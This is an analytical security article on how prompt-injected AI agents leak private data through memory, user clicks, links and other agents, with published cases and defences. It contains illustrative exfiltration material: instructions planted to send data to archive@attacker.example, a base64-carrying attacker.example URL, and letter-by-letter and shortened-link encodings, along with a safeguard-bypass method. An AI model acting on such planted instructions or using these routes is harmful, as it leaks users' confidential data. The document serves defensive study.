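A good classifier can label Rovo's tool and fetch_page correctly, but it has to treat every outgoing request as a possible message, as Snyk does when it counts HTTP requests as a way for data to leave. Missing such a tool is an ordinary labeling mistake.

Requests inside a tool's own code are harder to label. For example, a tool called convert_currency might have the description "Converts an amount from one currency to another." If an agent enters 41 million pounds as the amount, the tool's code sends that figure to an outside company that supplies exchange rates. The description does not mention a request, so a scanner that reads descriptions would find no sink. Someone who had read the code could add the label, but an operator usually cannot read the code of a server that another company runs, and that company can change the code without changing the description.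 Running the tool in a test environment and recording its network traffic gives better evidence, but only about the version tested. For a remote server, the recording covers only the traffic on the operator's side.

The sink label is least suited to information leaked through the agent's choices, because a tool either has the label or doesn't, regardless of how much it can leak. Before Anthropic's fix, a reviewer could have removed the label from Claude's web fetch tool because Claude could not write addresses, and TF001 would then have missed Paul's attack. Keeping the label would have been correct, but a tool that leaks a name letter by letter would then have had the same label as one that can send a whole document in a few requests.

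A tool that takes no arguments can still leak data through the agent's choice of when to call it. Suppose the assistant has a tool, check_status, that always requests the same page from an outside service. The agent cannot put anything into the request, but if the attacker can read the service's log, an injected instruction can tell the agent to call the tool once for every million in the Heron offer. If the offer is 41 million, the log will show 41 identical requests. The order and timing of calls can carry information in the same way. To catch every such leak, a reviewer would have to label as a sink any tool whose use an outsider can observe. The analysis would then flag every assistant that reads mail and uses even one outside service.

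## Memory that carries data and instructions between sessions

An operator who labels every tool correctly, including the read-only ones, can still miss a data theft that spans two sessions. Each session may lack one of the three roles, but memory carries what the attacker needs from the first session to the second.

### What counts as memory

Memory is anything the agent stores in one session and reads in a later one, whether or not the vendor calls it memory. In *What If Prompt Injection Never Left?*, Xie, Zhu and colleagues (2026) count retrieval stores, files, databases and the saved state of connected applications as memory, because an outsider's text can survive in any of them.

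| Kind of memory | How text gets in | How it comes back |
|---|---|---|
| Built-in memory feature | The model calls a memory tool, for example when the user says "remember" | The client often adds the whole list to each new conversation |
| Notes and instruction files | The agent edits a file in its workspace | The program loads the file at the start, or the agent opens it |
| Session summary | A separate process writes it | The program adds it to the instructions for later sessions |
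| Retrieval index | A program cuts up past conversations or documents and stores the pieces | A search selects the pieces most similar to the user's request |
| Shared document or application record | The agent, or anyone else with access, saves it | The agent opens it with an ordinary tool |

A tool graph can show memory only where the agent reads or writes it through a tool. Unit 42, the research team of the security company Palo Alto Networks, attacked a test agent on Amazon's Bedrock platform through its session summaries. Instructions from a malicious web page ended up in the summary, and in later sessions the agent silently sent out the user's conversation history. The summary is part of how the agent runs, so a scanner that lists tools would not list it.

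The kind of memory affects how often stored text reaches the model again. In tests by Xie and colleagues, text in a store that the program always loads reached the model every time, while text that the agent had to look up did so about half the time. Retrieval search offers little protection by itself because, as *The Price of Safety* (2026) points out, it ranks entries by similarity without checking whether they can be trusted. An attacker's entry can therefore rank as high as a real one.

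### Two sessions, neither with all three roles

Suppose the operator splits the office assistant's work so that TF001 stays quiet. In reading sessions, the assistant can open documents that the user has received from outside, and it can save notes. In writing sessions, it can search the user's files and send mail. The client loads the notes at the start of every session. The labels are:

λ(open_upload) = {untrusted}

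λ(save_note) = ∅

λ(search_files) = {private}

λ(send_mail) = {sink}

On Tuesday the user uploads a market report that an attacker has prepared and asks for a summary. Hidden text in the report makes the assistant save a false note that the user wants a copy of every deal summary sent to archive@attacker.example. The summary of the report looks normal. On Thursday the user asks the assistant to send a colleague a summary of the Heron file. The assistant follows its notes and sends the summary, which includes the offer price, to both the colleague and the attacker.

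Let L₁ and L₂ be the combined labels of the tools in the two sessions. Then

L₁ = {untrusted} and L₂ = {private, sink}.

Neither set is complete, so TF001 raises no warning for either session. The split also satisfies Meta's Agents Rule of Two, which allows an agent no more than two of three risky properties "within a session", unless the operator counts the notes as untrusted content. Counting them that way is correct and gives Thursday's session all three properties, but it requires the operator to know where the notes came from.

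Here the client loads the notes by itself, so there is no tool for a reviewer to label untrusted. If the assistant read its notes with a tool, a reviewer could label that tool untrusted, but TF001 would then warn about every writing session, even if no stranger's text had ever reached the notes. The label would also go against the usual view of memory. The Model Context Protocol gives a memory tool as its example of a tool that does not deal with the outside world.

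The note in this example is an instruction, but memory can also carry the private data itself, as in the earlier example of the file saved on Monday and published on Thursday. This kind of leak may need nothing malicious in the second session. *Ghost in the Agent* (Cai, Wen and colleagues, 2026) describes a test case in which an attacker gets an agent to store a confidential revenue forecast. Three days later the user asks for an operations report, and the agent retrieves the forecast and includes it. If the report goes to people who shouldn't see the forecast, the data have leaked through an ordinary request. A filter that searches memory for suspicious instructions would miss the forecast because it contains none.

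### Merging all sessions into one graph

A scanner could treat all sessions that share a memory as one and combine their labels. It would then catch the Heron theft, since L₁ ∪ L₂ contains all three roles. But it would also raise alarms for impossible thefts, because a document that the user uploads on Friday cannot affect mail sent on Thursday. A more careful rule only looks back. In session k, it raises the alarm if

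sink ∈ Lₖ and L₁ ∪ … ∪ Lₖ = {untrusted, private, sink}.

In ordinary use this refinement hardly helps. After the user has opened one outside document and searched the files once, every later session with send_mail triggers the alarm, even if the user only orders lunch. The operator can stop the alarms by erasing the memory, running some sessions without memory, or removing send_mail. The alarm doesn't indicate whether an attacker's text ever reached the memory.

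Cai and colleagues provide a rough idea of how many such alarms would be false. Their benchmark has 400 scenarios from 20 agent frameworks, and in half of them content from a source such as a web page or stored document influences a sensitive tool call. They tested FIDES, which follows labels through an agent's tool calls and, by their account, treats a path from a source to a sink as strong evidence of a flow. It raised 106 false alarms on the 200 scenarios without such a flow. It also missed 92 of the 200 real flows, in some cases because its labels were lost when a session ended.

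Cai and colleagues' own system, NeuroTaint, raised 16 false alarms and missed 13 flows. It stores a record of each text's source with the text and compares the meaning of inputs and outputs. It analyzes logs after the agent has finished, so it can find leaks but can't stop them.

The comparison comes from the developers of the better-scoring system. FIDES raised no alarms on four of the frameworks, which suggests their setup did not suit it there. On the other 16, it flagged 106 of 160 harmless scenarios, about two-thirds. A merged tool graph would probably do worse, because it flags a scenario whenever the tools are present, even if no path of actual calls connects them.

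### SpAIware

In 2024, Johann Rehberger demonstrated SpAIware, an attack that made ChatGPT's macOS app keep leaking conversations through an invisible image. His Embrace The Red post *Spyware Injection Into Your ChatGPT's Long-Term Memory (SpAIware)* describes how text on a website or in a document made the model call its memory tool and store the leaking instruction. ChatGPT included its memories in every new conversation, so the app sent every later message and reply to Rehberger's server.

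In the later conversations, the user typed the private data and the app loaded the image, so the leak required neither a private-data tool nor a sink tool. A scan of one of those conversations could have found only the memory tool.

The data left by an already known route, in which a client leaks data by loading an image from an attacker's address. To mitigate this, OpenAI introduced a check in December 2023 for whether an address is safe to display, but each client had to apply it. The web version did, but the iOS app did not, and the Android and macOS apps came out in 2024 with the same gap.

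In May 2024 Rehberger reported that websites could plant memories in ChatGPT, but OpenAI closed his ticket as a model safety issue rather than a security issue. In June he sent a demonstration of the full data theft, and OpenAI fixed the macOS app in September. The fix blocked the route used to send data out, but a website or document could still make ChatGPT store a memory. An instruction planted before the fix would presumably have stayed in the user's memory and worked again if another way to send data out appeared.

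### ZombieAgent and CoSnitch

*ZombieAgent* describes another way for data to leak, which the security company Radware reported in September 2025. By then, OpenAI had blocked chats from using memory after they had used connectors, which link ChatGPT to services such as Gmail. ChatGPT also refused to open an attacker's web addresses if they came from memory.

The first restriction worked in only one direction. ChatGPT could still read its memory and then use a connector in the same chat. Instructions in a shared file could also still change memory, so the attacker used a file that the user shared with ChatGPT to add two rules. The first was to read a certain email from the attacker whenever the user sent a message, and to carry out the instructions in it. The second was to save any sensitive information the user shared, so the memory collected private data alongside the attacker's rules as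 the user kept talking.

The second restriction failed because the addresses were in the email, not in memory. The email listed a ready-made address for each letter and digit, and ChatGPT spelled out the stolen text by opening these addresses one after another. Claude spelled out text the same way on Ayush Paul's coffee shop site the following year. Because the stored rule only pointed to an email, the attacker could presumably change the instructions by sending a new email. OpenAI fixed the flaw on December 16, 2025, 81 days after the first report. Radware gives the date of the fix but no details.

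Microsoft's Copilot Personal let web pages add to its memory. In Varonis' *CoSnitch* (2026), a user asks Copilot to summarize a page with hidden text, and Copilot saves the attacker's instruction to its memory while showing the user a normal summary. Copilot's memories had no expiry date, and the instruction would survive a password change or a new device until the user found it in the settings and deleted it.

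In CoSnitch, Copilot leaked data by fetching web pages. It put text from the victim's Gmail into a URL and requested that URL from the researchers' server. Varonis demonstrated this theft with a link that ran a prompt as soon as the victim clicked it, and demonstrated the memory write separately. In its example, a planted memory made Copilot describe a software vulnerability as harmless. An attacker could plausibly combine the two, but the published demonstrations do not include a stored instruction that later steals data.

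A scanner with correct labels would have raised an alarm for Copilot even without memory, since Gmail and web fetching together fill all three roles. But the victim could not learn from that alarm how to recover. Disconnecting Gmail would clear the alarm but leave the planted instruction in memory, where it could still take effect if the victim reconnected Gmail.

Varonis reported the flaws in December 2025, and Microsoft did not patch them until August 18, 2026. Microsoft made the repair on its own servers, and Varonis found no sign that attackers had used the flaws. TechRadar's *Experts manage to hack Microsoft Copilot by continually asking it questions* gives the severity as 8.8 out of 10 and notes that it is not known how Microsoft fixed the flaws.

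### How often a planted memory works

The vendors' cases show that these thefts are possible, and several 2026 studies measure how often they succeed. *Trojan Hippo Bench* (Das, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues, 2026) studied data theft directly. Beurer-Kellner, now at Snyk, had also helped demonstrate the GitHub exploit.

The test agent was an email assistant with one of four kinds of memory. It read a single email from the attacker, and the attack then lay dormant for up to 100 harmless sessions until the user sent a message that mentioned a sensitive subject, such as health or tax. The attack succeeded if the agent emailed all the personal details in that message to the attacker. A search program had refined each attack email over up to 40 rounds, and each success rate comes from 60 runs.

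After 100 sessions, the attack succeeded in 80% to 100% of runs with Gemini 3.1 Pro, depending on the kind of memory, and in 15% to 85% with GPT-5-mini. The rates for Gemini did not decline steadily as the number of sessions grew. TF001 would have flagged this assistant because it could read and send mail in the same session, so the experiment measures how dangerous memory is, not how often a scanner would miss it. The search assumed that the attacker knew the agent's system prompt and type of memory, which favors the attack. However, an attacker can learn much of this by testing a copy of a public product.

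Pulipaka, Hlebik and colleagues (2026), in *Hidden in Memory*, planted false memories about the user by means of documents such as news articles and legal filings. Where the model controlled its own memory tool, the results depended heavily on the model and on the attacker's aim:

| Purpose of the false memory | Stored by GPT-5.5 | Stored by Claude Sonnet 4.6 |
|---|---|---|
| To change what the assistant says or believes | 99.8% | 64.2% |
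| To change what the agent does, for example with files | 91.5% | 6.5% |

Data theft was among the harder aims to plant in memory. Across all steps from the document to the harmful action, between 3% and 66% of attacks on agents succeeded when the later task was related to the memory, and at most 5% succeeded when it was unrelated.

The effect of the later task helps explain why planted instructions worked less often over time in another study. *MemoryDojo* (Yang, Bullwinkel and colleagues, 2026) ran 155 series of tasks on five memory systems, mostly with the model GPT-5.6 Luna. An instruction planted in one tool result led the agent to do what the attacker wanted at least once in 15% to 46% of the series, depending on the memory system, and in 30% to 71% after an optimizer had improved the wording. In longer series that mixed different kinds of work, the attack succeeded less often over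 time on four of the five systems. Filling each memory with about 48 harmless conversations beforehand reduced success further, to zero on one system, though on another the attack still worked at least once in 45% of runs.

Yang and colleagues counted every later task, while Das and colleagues tested only the session in which the user raised the attacker's chosen subject. The second measure is closer to the real risk of data theft, because an attacker who wants tax records loses nothing if the instruction does no harm until the user asks about tax.

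Yang and colleagues also found that when an agent acts on a planted instruction, it may record what it did and so write the instruction into memory again. On the memory system A-MEM, after the optimizer had improved the attack, 63% of the sessions that retrieved poisoned text retrieved at least one of these later entries. Deleting the original entry would not have removed the instruction in those cases. *Bad Memory* (2026) found that models that refused to carry out a malicious instruction sometimes still left it in their memory files, where a later session or a weaker model could act on it.

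Xie and colleagues ran 486 two-session cases on five models, and 41.9% of the attacks succeeded from start to finish. Planted falsehoods worked far more often (73.6%) than attempts to change the agent's actions (35.5%). The best of four widely used general filters for prompt injection detected only 14.8% of the attacks in the session where the text came in and 36.2% in the session where it took effect. These low rates are reasonable for filters that examine one exchange at a time, since a sentence about where to send copies looks much like a real preference.

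### Asking the user before each write

A client could ask the user to approve every new memory. In the Heron example, this would give the user a fair chance of noticing the problem on Tuesday, because they asked only for a summary of a report and the note is about sending deal summaries to an unknown address. The client would have to show the note's exact text and name the document it came from, not just display a message such as "Memory updated".

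User approval works for a short list of facts that the model occasionally adds to, but it is impractical for session summaries and retrieval indexes, which store text after every conversation. Users also tire of approval requests, as Invariant Labs observed of people who choose "Always Allow". Even a user who reads every entry may approve one that contains stolen data, because *StegoMemory* (2026) describes how an innocent-looking entry can carry a secret message that a receiver recovers in a later session.

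### Keeping outside text away from memory

OpenAI's separation of memory from connectors was sensible but covered too few cases. Das and colleagues tested stricter versions of it and two other defenses. The figures below are for Gemini 3.1 Pro with a retrieval index, measured 100 sessions after the attack. The last column is the average success rate on seven kinds of harmless work.

| Defense | Successful attacks | Harmless tasks completed |
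|---|---|---|
| None | 85% | 99% |
| Store only what the user writes | 5% | 89% |
| Store nothing once a session has read outside content | 5% | 71% |
| Cut each entry to 80 characters | 30% | 89% |
| Label entries by origin and block sending in any session that has read outside content or loaded such an entry | 0% | 71% |

Either of the first two rules would have kept the false note out of the Heron assistant's memory. But with the two defenses that averaged 71%, at least one kind of work failed completely. An assistant that cannot store anything after reading mail cannot remember a new phone number from a client's message, and an operator whose users need that will turn the rule off.

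These rules also address stored data less well than stored instructions. A memory that contains only the user's own words can still include their salary or medical history, and an attacker can use an injection in a later session to request it. Reading such a memory should therefore count as access to private data, even in a session with no tool for accessing private data.

### Recording where each memory came from

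The remaining approach lets the agent store outside text but keeps a label with it. On Tuesday the note would get the label {untrusted}. When the client loaded it on Thursday, the session would take on the note's label, and its labels would become

L₂ ∪ λ(note) = {private, sink} ∪ {untrusted},

which is all three. TF001's formula would then raise the alarm, and a program that enforced the rule could stop the mail. This is more precise than merging the sessions, because Tuesday's document matters only if something derived from it comes back.

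The label has to survive summarizing, rewriting and the end of the session. *MemLineage* (2026) attaches it to the memory entry itself, and a system called SPA keeps labels from one query to the next. The label also needs protection against forgery. According to *MemLineage*, NeuroTaint has no such protection, so an attacker who can write to the memory store unnoticed could relabel an entry as trusted. The proof behind the 0% in the table assumes that labels spread to everything derived from outside text. Das and colleagues note that the proof does not cover an agent that copies such text into an entry without the label.

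Recording the origin of a memory does not prevent leaks unless a rule acts on that record. *Securing LLM-Agent Long-Term Memory Against Poisoning* (2026) repeated the Trojan Hippo attack against a lineage-based defense, and 78.5% of attempts succeeded, the same as with no defense. The defense checked for conflicts with values already on record, and the attacker's address did not conflict with any. The paper's own system refuses to send data to an address of untrusted origin unless a trusted source has confirmed it. This system blocked all 1,152 attempts in reproductions of four published attacks, and the agent completed as many harmless tasks as it did without it.

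The choice of rule matters most when the client loads every note into every session. A single note from an outside document then marks all later sessions as untrusted. A rule that blocks sending in untrusted sessions would stop the Heron assistant from mailing anyone until someone deleted the note. A rule based on the recipient's address would block only the copy to archive@attacker.example and let the colleague's mail through.

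## Flows through the user

A tool graph has no node for the user, so it cannot show data that enters or leaves through the user. A stranger's text can get into the user's messages through a link or the clipboard. Storing only what the user writes, which was one of the stronger defenses against planted memories, assumes that the user wrote everything in those messages. Data can also leave when the user clicks, pastes or forwards something the agent produced.

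### Links that carry a prompt

Samoilenko's website put instructions into ChatGPT in 2023 by adding them to text that visitors copied. A link can do the same with less effort from the victim. Many assistants accept a prompt as part of a web address, as in this harmless example:

```
https://assistant.example/?q=Summarize+this+article
```

When someone opens the address, the assistant's page loads in that person's logged-in session and puts the text after `q=` into the input box. Some products have also submitted the text immediately. Websites use this feature for "Summarize with AI" buttons. The model receives the text as a message from the user, even if someone else wrote it.

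Businesses already exploit this for advertising. In 60 days of email traffic, Microsoft (2026) found 50 different prompts from 31 companies that told an assistant to remember the company, for example as a trusted source. None of the senders was a criminal group, and the prompts' effect varied between assistants. The count shows that ready-made tools for building such links are in wide use, but not that data theft by this route is common.

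Suppose the operator of the office assistant takes away every tool that could return an outsider's text. The assistant can search files that the user wrote and can send mail:

λ(search_files) = {private}

λ(send_mail) = {sink}

TF001 finds only two of the required roles, so it raises no warning. The user then clicks a link in an ordinary mail program. The link submits a user message that instructs the agent to send the Heron file to archive@attacker.example, and this message supplies the missing role.

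Labeling the user {untrusted} would cause constant false alarms, and so would labeling every chat window a sink. Labeling individual messages is more precise. The client can detect whether a message came from the keyboard, the clipboard or a link, so it could label only messages from links {untrusted}. All three roles would then be present only in sessions that contain such a message.

### Reprompt

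Varonis' *Reprompt* (2026) describes a theft of this kind from Copilot Personal, the consumer version of Microsoft's assistant. The victim needed to click only once, on a link to Microsoft's real site, and the attack worked in four steps:

1. The link opened Copilot in the victim's session, and Copilot ran the attacker's prompt from the address.
2. The prompt told Copilot to put a fact about the user into an address on the attacker's server and fetch it.
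3. Copilot's safeguard removed private data from the first such request. It did not check later ones, so the prompt had Copilot make every request twice.
4. The attacker's server answered each request with a new instruction, which could build on what Copilot had already revealed.

Ars Technica's *A single click mounted a covert, multistage attack against Copilot* (2026) reports that the researchers obtained the user's name, location and details of events from the chat history. The theft continued even after the chat was closed. Inspecting the link beforehand would not have revealed what it would steal, because the later instructions were on the server.

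According to BeyondMachines, Varonis reported the flaw on August 31, 2025, and Microsoft patched it 135 days later, on January 13, 2026. Reprompt did not affect business customers of Microsoft 365 Copilot, but SearchLeak later entered that product, also through a link.

The attack needed no plugins or connected accounts. The labels {untrusted, sink} fit Copilot's ability to fetch pages. But if the client supplied the user's details and chat history without a tool call, a scanner would have found no private-data tool, and TF001 would not have triggered.

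In CoSnitch, the later attack on the same product, the `q` parameter only filled in the input box, so the user still had to press Enter. Varonis found a second, undocumented parameter that submitted the prompt automatically. The prompt could then search the victim's connected mail, files and calendar, although Copilot was built on the assumption that only users start such searches.

*RovoBlast* (Varonis, 2026) disclosed a similar flaw in Atlassian's Rovo in August. One click on a link put the attacker's prompt into Rovo Chat, with no warning or label showing that the session had started from outside. Rovo could search company documents and connected services such as Slack, and its research agent could send data out by browsing the web. Varonis rarely had to get around any safeguard. Atlassian has fixed the flaw. A scanner with correct labels would have flagged Rovo anyway, but if an administrator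 had responded by disconnecting every source of outside text, the attack through the link would still have worked.

### Defenses that trust the user's message

Some defenses against injection give the user's messages more authority than other text. Claude Code's auto mode, for example, replaces most approval prompts with a classifier, a model that allows or blocks each action. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* explains that the classifier receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls but not the tool results. An instruction planted in a web page therefore can't influence the classifier directly.

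If the user pastes that instruction into the chat, however, the classifier treats it as the user's own request. Anthropic limits the damage by specifying that the classifier should never approve exfiltration, regardless of the user's messages.

ChatGPT's check on exact addresses has a similar exception. As Embrace The Red understands it, an address that appears in the user's message counts as safe for the rest of the chat. Text that the user pastes could therefore supply the addresses used to spell out private data, as the attacker's email did in ZombieAgent.

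### Links that wait for a click

In the other direction, the agent puts private data in a link's address, and the user sends the data by clicking the link. In the Heron example, a link with an innocent label, such as "Open the market report", replaces the image, and the browser requests the address only when the user clicks.

*Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents*, by the security company Checkmarx, examined both forms in Microsoft's Copilot Chat and Google's Gemini. Checkmarx demonstrated the image form in Copilot Chat by taking an API key from a developer's environment. Gemini does not display external images, which stops that form, but it still displays links. Google removes only links that its Safe Browsing service has already flagged as malicious, so an attacker can use a newly registered domain.

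| Product and route | User's part, once the agent has read the attacker's text | Vendor's decision |
|---|---|---|
| Gemini, image | None | Google blocks external images |
| Gemini, link | One click | "Won't Fix (Infeasible)", October 9, 2025 |
| Copilot Chat, image | None | Microsoft closed the report without a fix, November 4, 2025 |

Google told Checkmarx that the link problem was not severe enough to track as a security bug. Checkmarx accepted this but wanted Google to warn users, who now have to manage the risk. Microsoft replied that the attack required several non-default actions by the user, did not work reliably and came with warnings. Microsoft also assumes that people at work review the code they choose to run. Checkmarx was probably counting clicks after the agent had read the malicious page, while Microsoft was probably counting the steps needed to get that far. Checkmarx concedes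 that getting an agent to read the page can be complex. It expects Microsoft to leave the link form of the attack unfixed too.

Microsoft's rules can cover attacks that need a click. Its severity scale for AI systems rates theft of another user's data as "Critical" if it needs no interaction and "Important" if it needs one or more clicks, and the company fixed Reprompt. Google's reward program for AI flaws covers attacks that leak sensitive information "without user approval", according to SecurityWeek, so whether an attack qualifies depends largely on what counts as approval.

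### Pasting and forwarding

Pasting a reply into another app can send data before anyone clicks a link. *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks* (Willison, 2024) explains that Slack and Discord fetch any address in a message to show a title and a picture. Suppose the user copies the assistant's summary, with its link, into a private Slack channel. Only colleagues can read the channel, but Slack requests the address, which sends the offer price to the attacker's log. Apps that post messages can turn these previews off, but a person who pastes text may not think to do so.

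When people talk to an agent inside a chat app, data can leak without the user pasting anything. PromptArmor found that OpenClaw, an agent people can use through Telegram, was exposed to such leaks by default because Telegram previewed the links in the agent's replies.

A forwarded document can leak data without any web request. Suppose Heron's owners are negotiating with the assistant's user and email a spreadsheet to complete. The email contains an injected instruction to copy the highest price the user would pay into a hidden column. The assistant fills in the spreadsheet, and the user checks the visible columns and sends the file back from an ordinary mail program. The spreadsheet tool doesn't send anything, so a reviewer would not label it a sink. An allowlist would not help either, because the file goes to the people the user chose.

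### Is a click consent?

A vendor who declines to fix such a leak can argue that the user released the data. Confidentiality, as defined earlier, requires R(r) ⊆ E: the recipients of a request must all be entitled to its data. On the consent argument, a click adds the recipients to the entitled group:

E′ = E ∪ R(r).

R(r) is then always part of E′, so no request that a user clicks on or approves could ever count as a leak. This conclusion is reasonable only if three premises hold:

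1. The user sees what data will be sent.
2. The user understands who will receive it.
3. The user intends to send that data to that recipient.

Consider first a hidden query string, the text after the question mark in a link's address. The user sees "Open the market report", but the address behind it is:

```
https://attacker.example/report?id=NDEgbWlsbGlvbg==
```

The last part of the address is "41 million" in base64, a standard way of writing data as letters and digits. Varonis also used base64 in CoSnitch. The first premise fails because even a user who inspects the address can't recognize the price. The second holds only to the extent that a domain name identifies its owner. The third fails because the user wants to read a report.

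A shortened link, which is a brief address that redirects to a longer one, is worse. The attacker's email could list 100 of them, one for each whole million from 1 to 100 million, and tell the agent to include the one that matches the price in the Heron file. The agent's choice reveals the price to the nearest million, which is log₂ 100 ≈ 6.6 bits of information. The link contains no private text, even in encoded form, and its domain belongs to the shortening service instead of the attacker, so none of the premises holds.

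An approval prompt can satisfy all three only if it displays the right information and the user reads it. A prompt for send_mail can show the address, the message and any attachments, but a prompt for a shell command usually shows the command without its effects. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) gives the example of `python3 setup.py`, which looks routine but runs whatever code the script contains. According to *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (2026), the information needed to judge an action may lie outside the action. Other research has shown that an agent can execute something different from what the user approved, and Checkmarx has demonstrated a way to defeat approval dialogs, which it calls Lies-in-the-Loop.

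| Case | Does the user see the data? | Know the recipient? | Intend the transfer? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Hidden query string | No | Only the domain name | No |
| Shortened link | No | No | No |
| Approval of an email | If the prompt shows all of it | If the prompt shows the address | If the user reads the prompt |
| Approval of a command | Often not | Often not | If the user works out what the command does |

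### How often people check

Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports the largest test of whether people read approval prompts. A research vendor gave 1,053 paid testers coding work and, partway through, replaced one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 of them (13.6%) refused it. Testers blocked about 17% of such commands early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts. Auto mode's classifier blocked 89% of the same commands.

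Anthropic published these figures to justify making the classifier the default. The testers were not working on their own projects, so they had less to lose than a real user, and the danger also went beyond data theft. Even so, approval prompts could count as reliable consent only if the result were wrong by a wide margin, and the decline within a session is consistent with people no longer reading the prompts.

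Claude Code's users approve 97% of permission prompts, up from 93% in Anthropic's earlier account. This rate alone proves little, because most commands are harmless. It matters more that 62% of users had either bypassed the prompts or told the program not to ask again about shell commands. In *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files*, user review contributed to 105 of 290 reported problems. Automatic approval played a part in 80 reports and an uninformative prompt in 31.

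*Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of software practitioners, suggests that repeated approval may reflect habit, fatigue or a need to keep work moving rather than growing trust. After one interviewee refused several requests, the agent tried another approach, and the interviewee could not tell whether it still respected the boundary they had set.

*Invisible Ink Threats* (2026) found that asking a simulated novice user for confirmation made attacks succeed more often, because the user's "yes" authorized the attacker's goal.

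People are somewhat more careful when a question is plainly about their data. *Towards Automating Data Access Permissions in AI Agents* (2025) had participants train an imaginary personal assistant and found that they granted both too much access and too little. About 95% allowed automatic sharing at least once, according to Help Net Security's *How researchers are teaching AI agents to ask for permission*. When the assistant brought in data that the task did not need, the share who chose "share always" fell from about 83% to 74%.

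### What a release should show

A system should still let people send out their own data. The buyer has to tell Heron's owners the offer price at some point, and an assistant that refused to send it would be useless for the deal. *Architecting Secure AI Agents* (2026) argues that even a theoretically perfect model could not resolve a user's ambiguous wish without asking them. Some confirmation steps therefore have to remain, and whether the consent argument holds depends on how they are designed.

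ChatGPT already does part of this. When its check on exact addresses, Safe Url, stops a request, ChatGPT may show the user the information that would be sent and ask for confirmation, according to OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026). The dialog for an unverified link warns that the address may share data from the conversation and shows the address. This is clearly better than a bare link, but if the dialog shows only the raw address, a user who sees `NDEgbWlsbGlvbg==` still does not know that it contains the offer price.

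A more useful dialog for the Heron link would read:

```
Send this information to attacker.example?

Data:       "41 million", from the file "Heron offer"
Recipient:  a site you have not used before
Requested:  by an email from an unknown sender
```

The first two lines address the first two premises. The last line helps with the third, because a user who asked for a summary of the day's mail can see that someone else wanted the transfer. To fill in these lines, the client needs to know which file the data came from and who wrote the text that requested the transfer. It must also send exactly what it displayed, or the user will have approved a different request from the one sent.

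This design doesn't work for shortened links. To find out where one leads, the client has to request it, and that request may reveal to the attacker which of the 100 links the agent chose. The client should therefore disable any shortened link that the user did not supply. Links from a prompt-carrying address or pasted text should not count as supplied by the user.

Such a dialog also has to be rare. OpenAI warns that frequent false alarms train people to click through without thinking. Claude Code's users reject 39% of the plans the agent presents for approval but only 3% of single permission requests. They may reject a plan because they dislike the design rather than because they see a danger, but the difference suggests that people exercise judgment when a question is infrequent and about something they understand. A client could let routine mail to colleagues through and ask only when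 private data would go to a new recipient.

When a link supplies a prompt, the client should display it and wait for the user to press Enter. People may approve this too without reading it, so the client should keep treating the text as untrusted after the user submits it. Varonis recommends applying controls to such input throughout the task, including to repeated requests, which would have closed the gap that Reprompt used.

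The warning about the spreadsheet has to come earlier, because the user sends it from a mail program that the agent's client does not control. When the assistant hands over the spreadsheet, the client could list the documents whose contents went into it and point out any hidden columns. A user who expected only published figures would then see the Heron file on the list before attaching the spreadsheet to an email.

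## Flows through other agents

An agent can also pass private data to another agent, whose tools a scanner lists in a separate graph. The second agent may then send the data out with a tool that looked harmless when the scanner checked that agent alone.

### How agents pass work on

A main agent can start a subagent, which is another run of a language model with its own instructions and tools. The main agent writes a task in plain language, the subagent carries it out, and its answer is added to the text the main agent is working on. A subagent may appear in the main agent's list of tools as just another entry. In *OMNI-LEAK*, Naik, Culligan and colleagues (2026) built such a system around an orchestrator, a main agent that divides a request into parts and assigns them. Its list had separate entries for an agent that queried a database and an agent that sent email. Neither agent had information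 about the other's existence.

Agents that belong to different organizations can exchange work through Agent2Agent (A2A), a protocol that Google introduced in April 2025 and handed to the Linux Foundation that June. As *A2ABreak* (Lotfi, Rahman and colleagues, 2026) describes it, a client agent first fetches the remote agent's card, a file that gives its identity, skills, address and login requirements. The client then logs in and sends a message. The remote agent either replies at once or opens a task, which it may pause to ask for more information. Unlike MCP, which connects an agent to tools that its operator controls, A2A connects it to another agent whose tools, memory and reasoning are hidden by design.

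Agents can also affect each other without exchanging messages, through any file, ticket or repository that one writes and another reads. Willison notes that companies often connect Zendesk, a customer support system, to the ticket tracker Jira, so that a customer's email automatically becomes a Jira ticket. Suppose a support agent adds the customer's account details to the ticket, and a coding agent later opens it. The coding agent then receives a stranger's text and private data through the ticket, even though neither agent's settings mention the other.

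### Two agents that each pass a scan

Call the office assistant A and the second agent, which receives its summaries and posts to a public website, B. Suppose A sends a summary every evening, and B puts whatever is meant for the public on the company's news page. Separate scans give them these labels:

L_A = λ(read_mail) ∪ λ(search_files) = {untrusted, private}

L_B = λ(post_page) = {sink}

TF001 raises no warning for either agent. An attacker then emails the user an instruction to look up the Heron offer and add it to the evening summary under the heading "For the news page". Agent A reads the email, searches the files and writes the summary. Agent B posts the price, and the attacker reads it on the company's website.

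A may need a tool to send the summary, but a reviewer would leave that tool unlabeled, as with mail_self, because it reaches only another of the company's own agents. If the reviewer marks B's incoming messages {untrusted}, B has the labels {untrusted, sink} and still passes. The analysis flags B only if the reviewer also marks the messages {private}, and B's own tools give the reviewer no reason to do so.

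Agents often leak private data to one another without revealing it in their final answer, according to *AgentLeak* (El Yagoubi, Badu-Marfo and Al Mallah, 2026). The study ran 1,000 scenarios from healthcare, finance, law and business on five models and looked for private data that the task did not require. Such data appeared in messages between agents in 68.8% of runs, in shared memory in 46.7%, and in final answers in 27.2%. In one healthcare workflow, a scheduling agent sent a patient's complete medical record to another agent, then returned an appointment confirmation that contained no unnecessary private data.

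These figures count needless sharing inside a system, most of which no attacker would see, and the models were of the GPT-4o generation. Splitting the work among agents also made leaks in the final answers less frequent than the 43.2% rate for a single agent. But the results show that an agent with no tool for accessing private data may well hold such data because another agent sent it.

### Stealing a database through three agents

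The system that Naik and colleagues built has the same arrangement of labels as A and B. Its database had a public table of employees and a private table with their Social Security numbers. The database agent could read the private table only while a privileged user was asking. An attacker without that privilege planted an instruction in a text field of the public table, and the theft took four steps:

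1. A privileged user asked a harmless question, such as which department Mark worked in.
2. The database agent read the planted text along with the answer and fetched all the Social Security numbers.
3. It returned the numbers to the orchestrator with a request to send them to a certain address.
4. The orchestrator passed the request to the email agent, which sent the numbers to the attacker.

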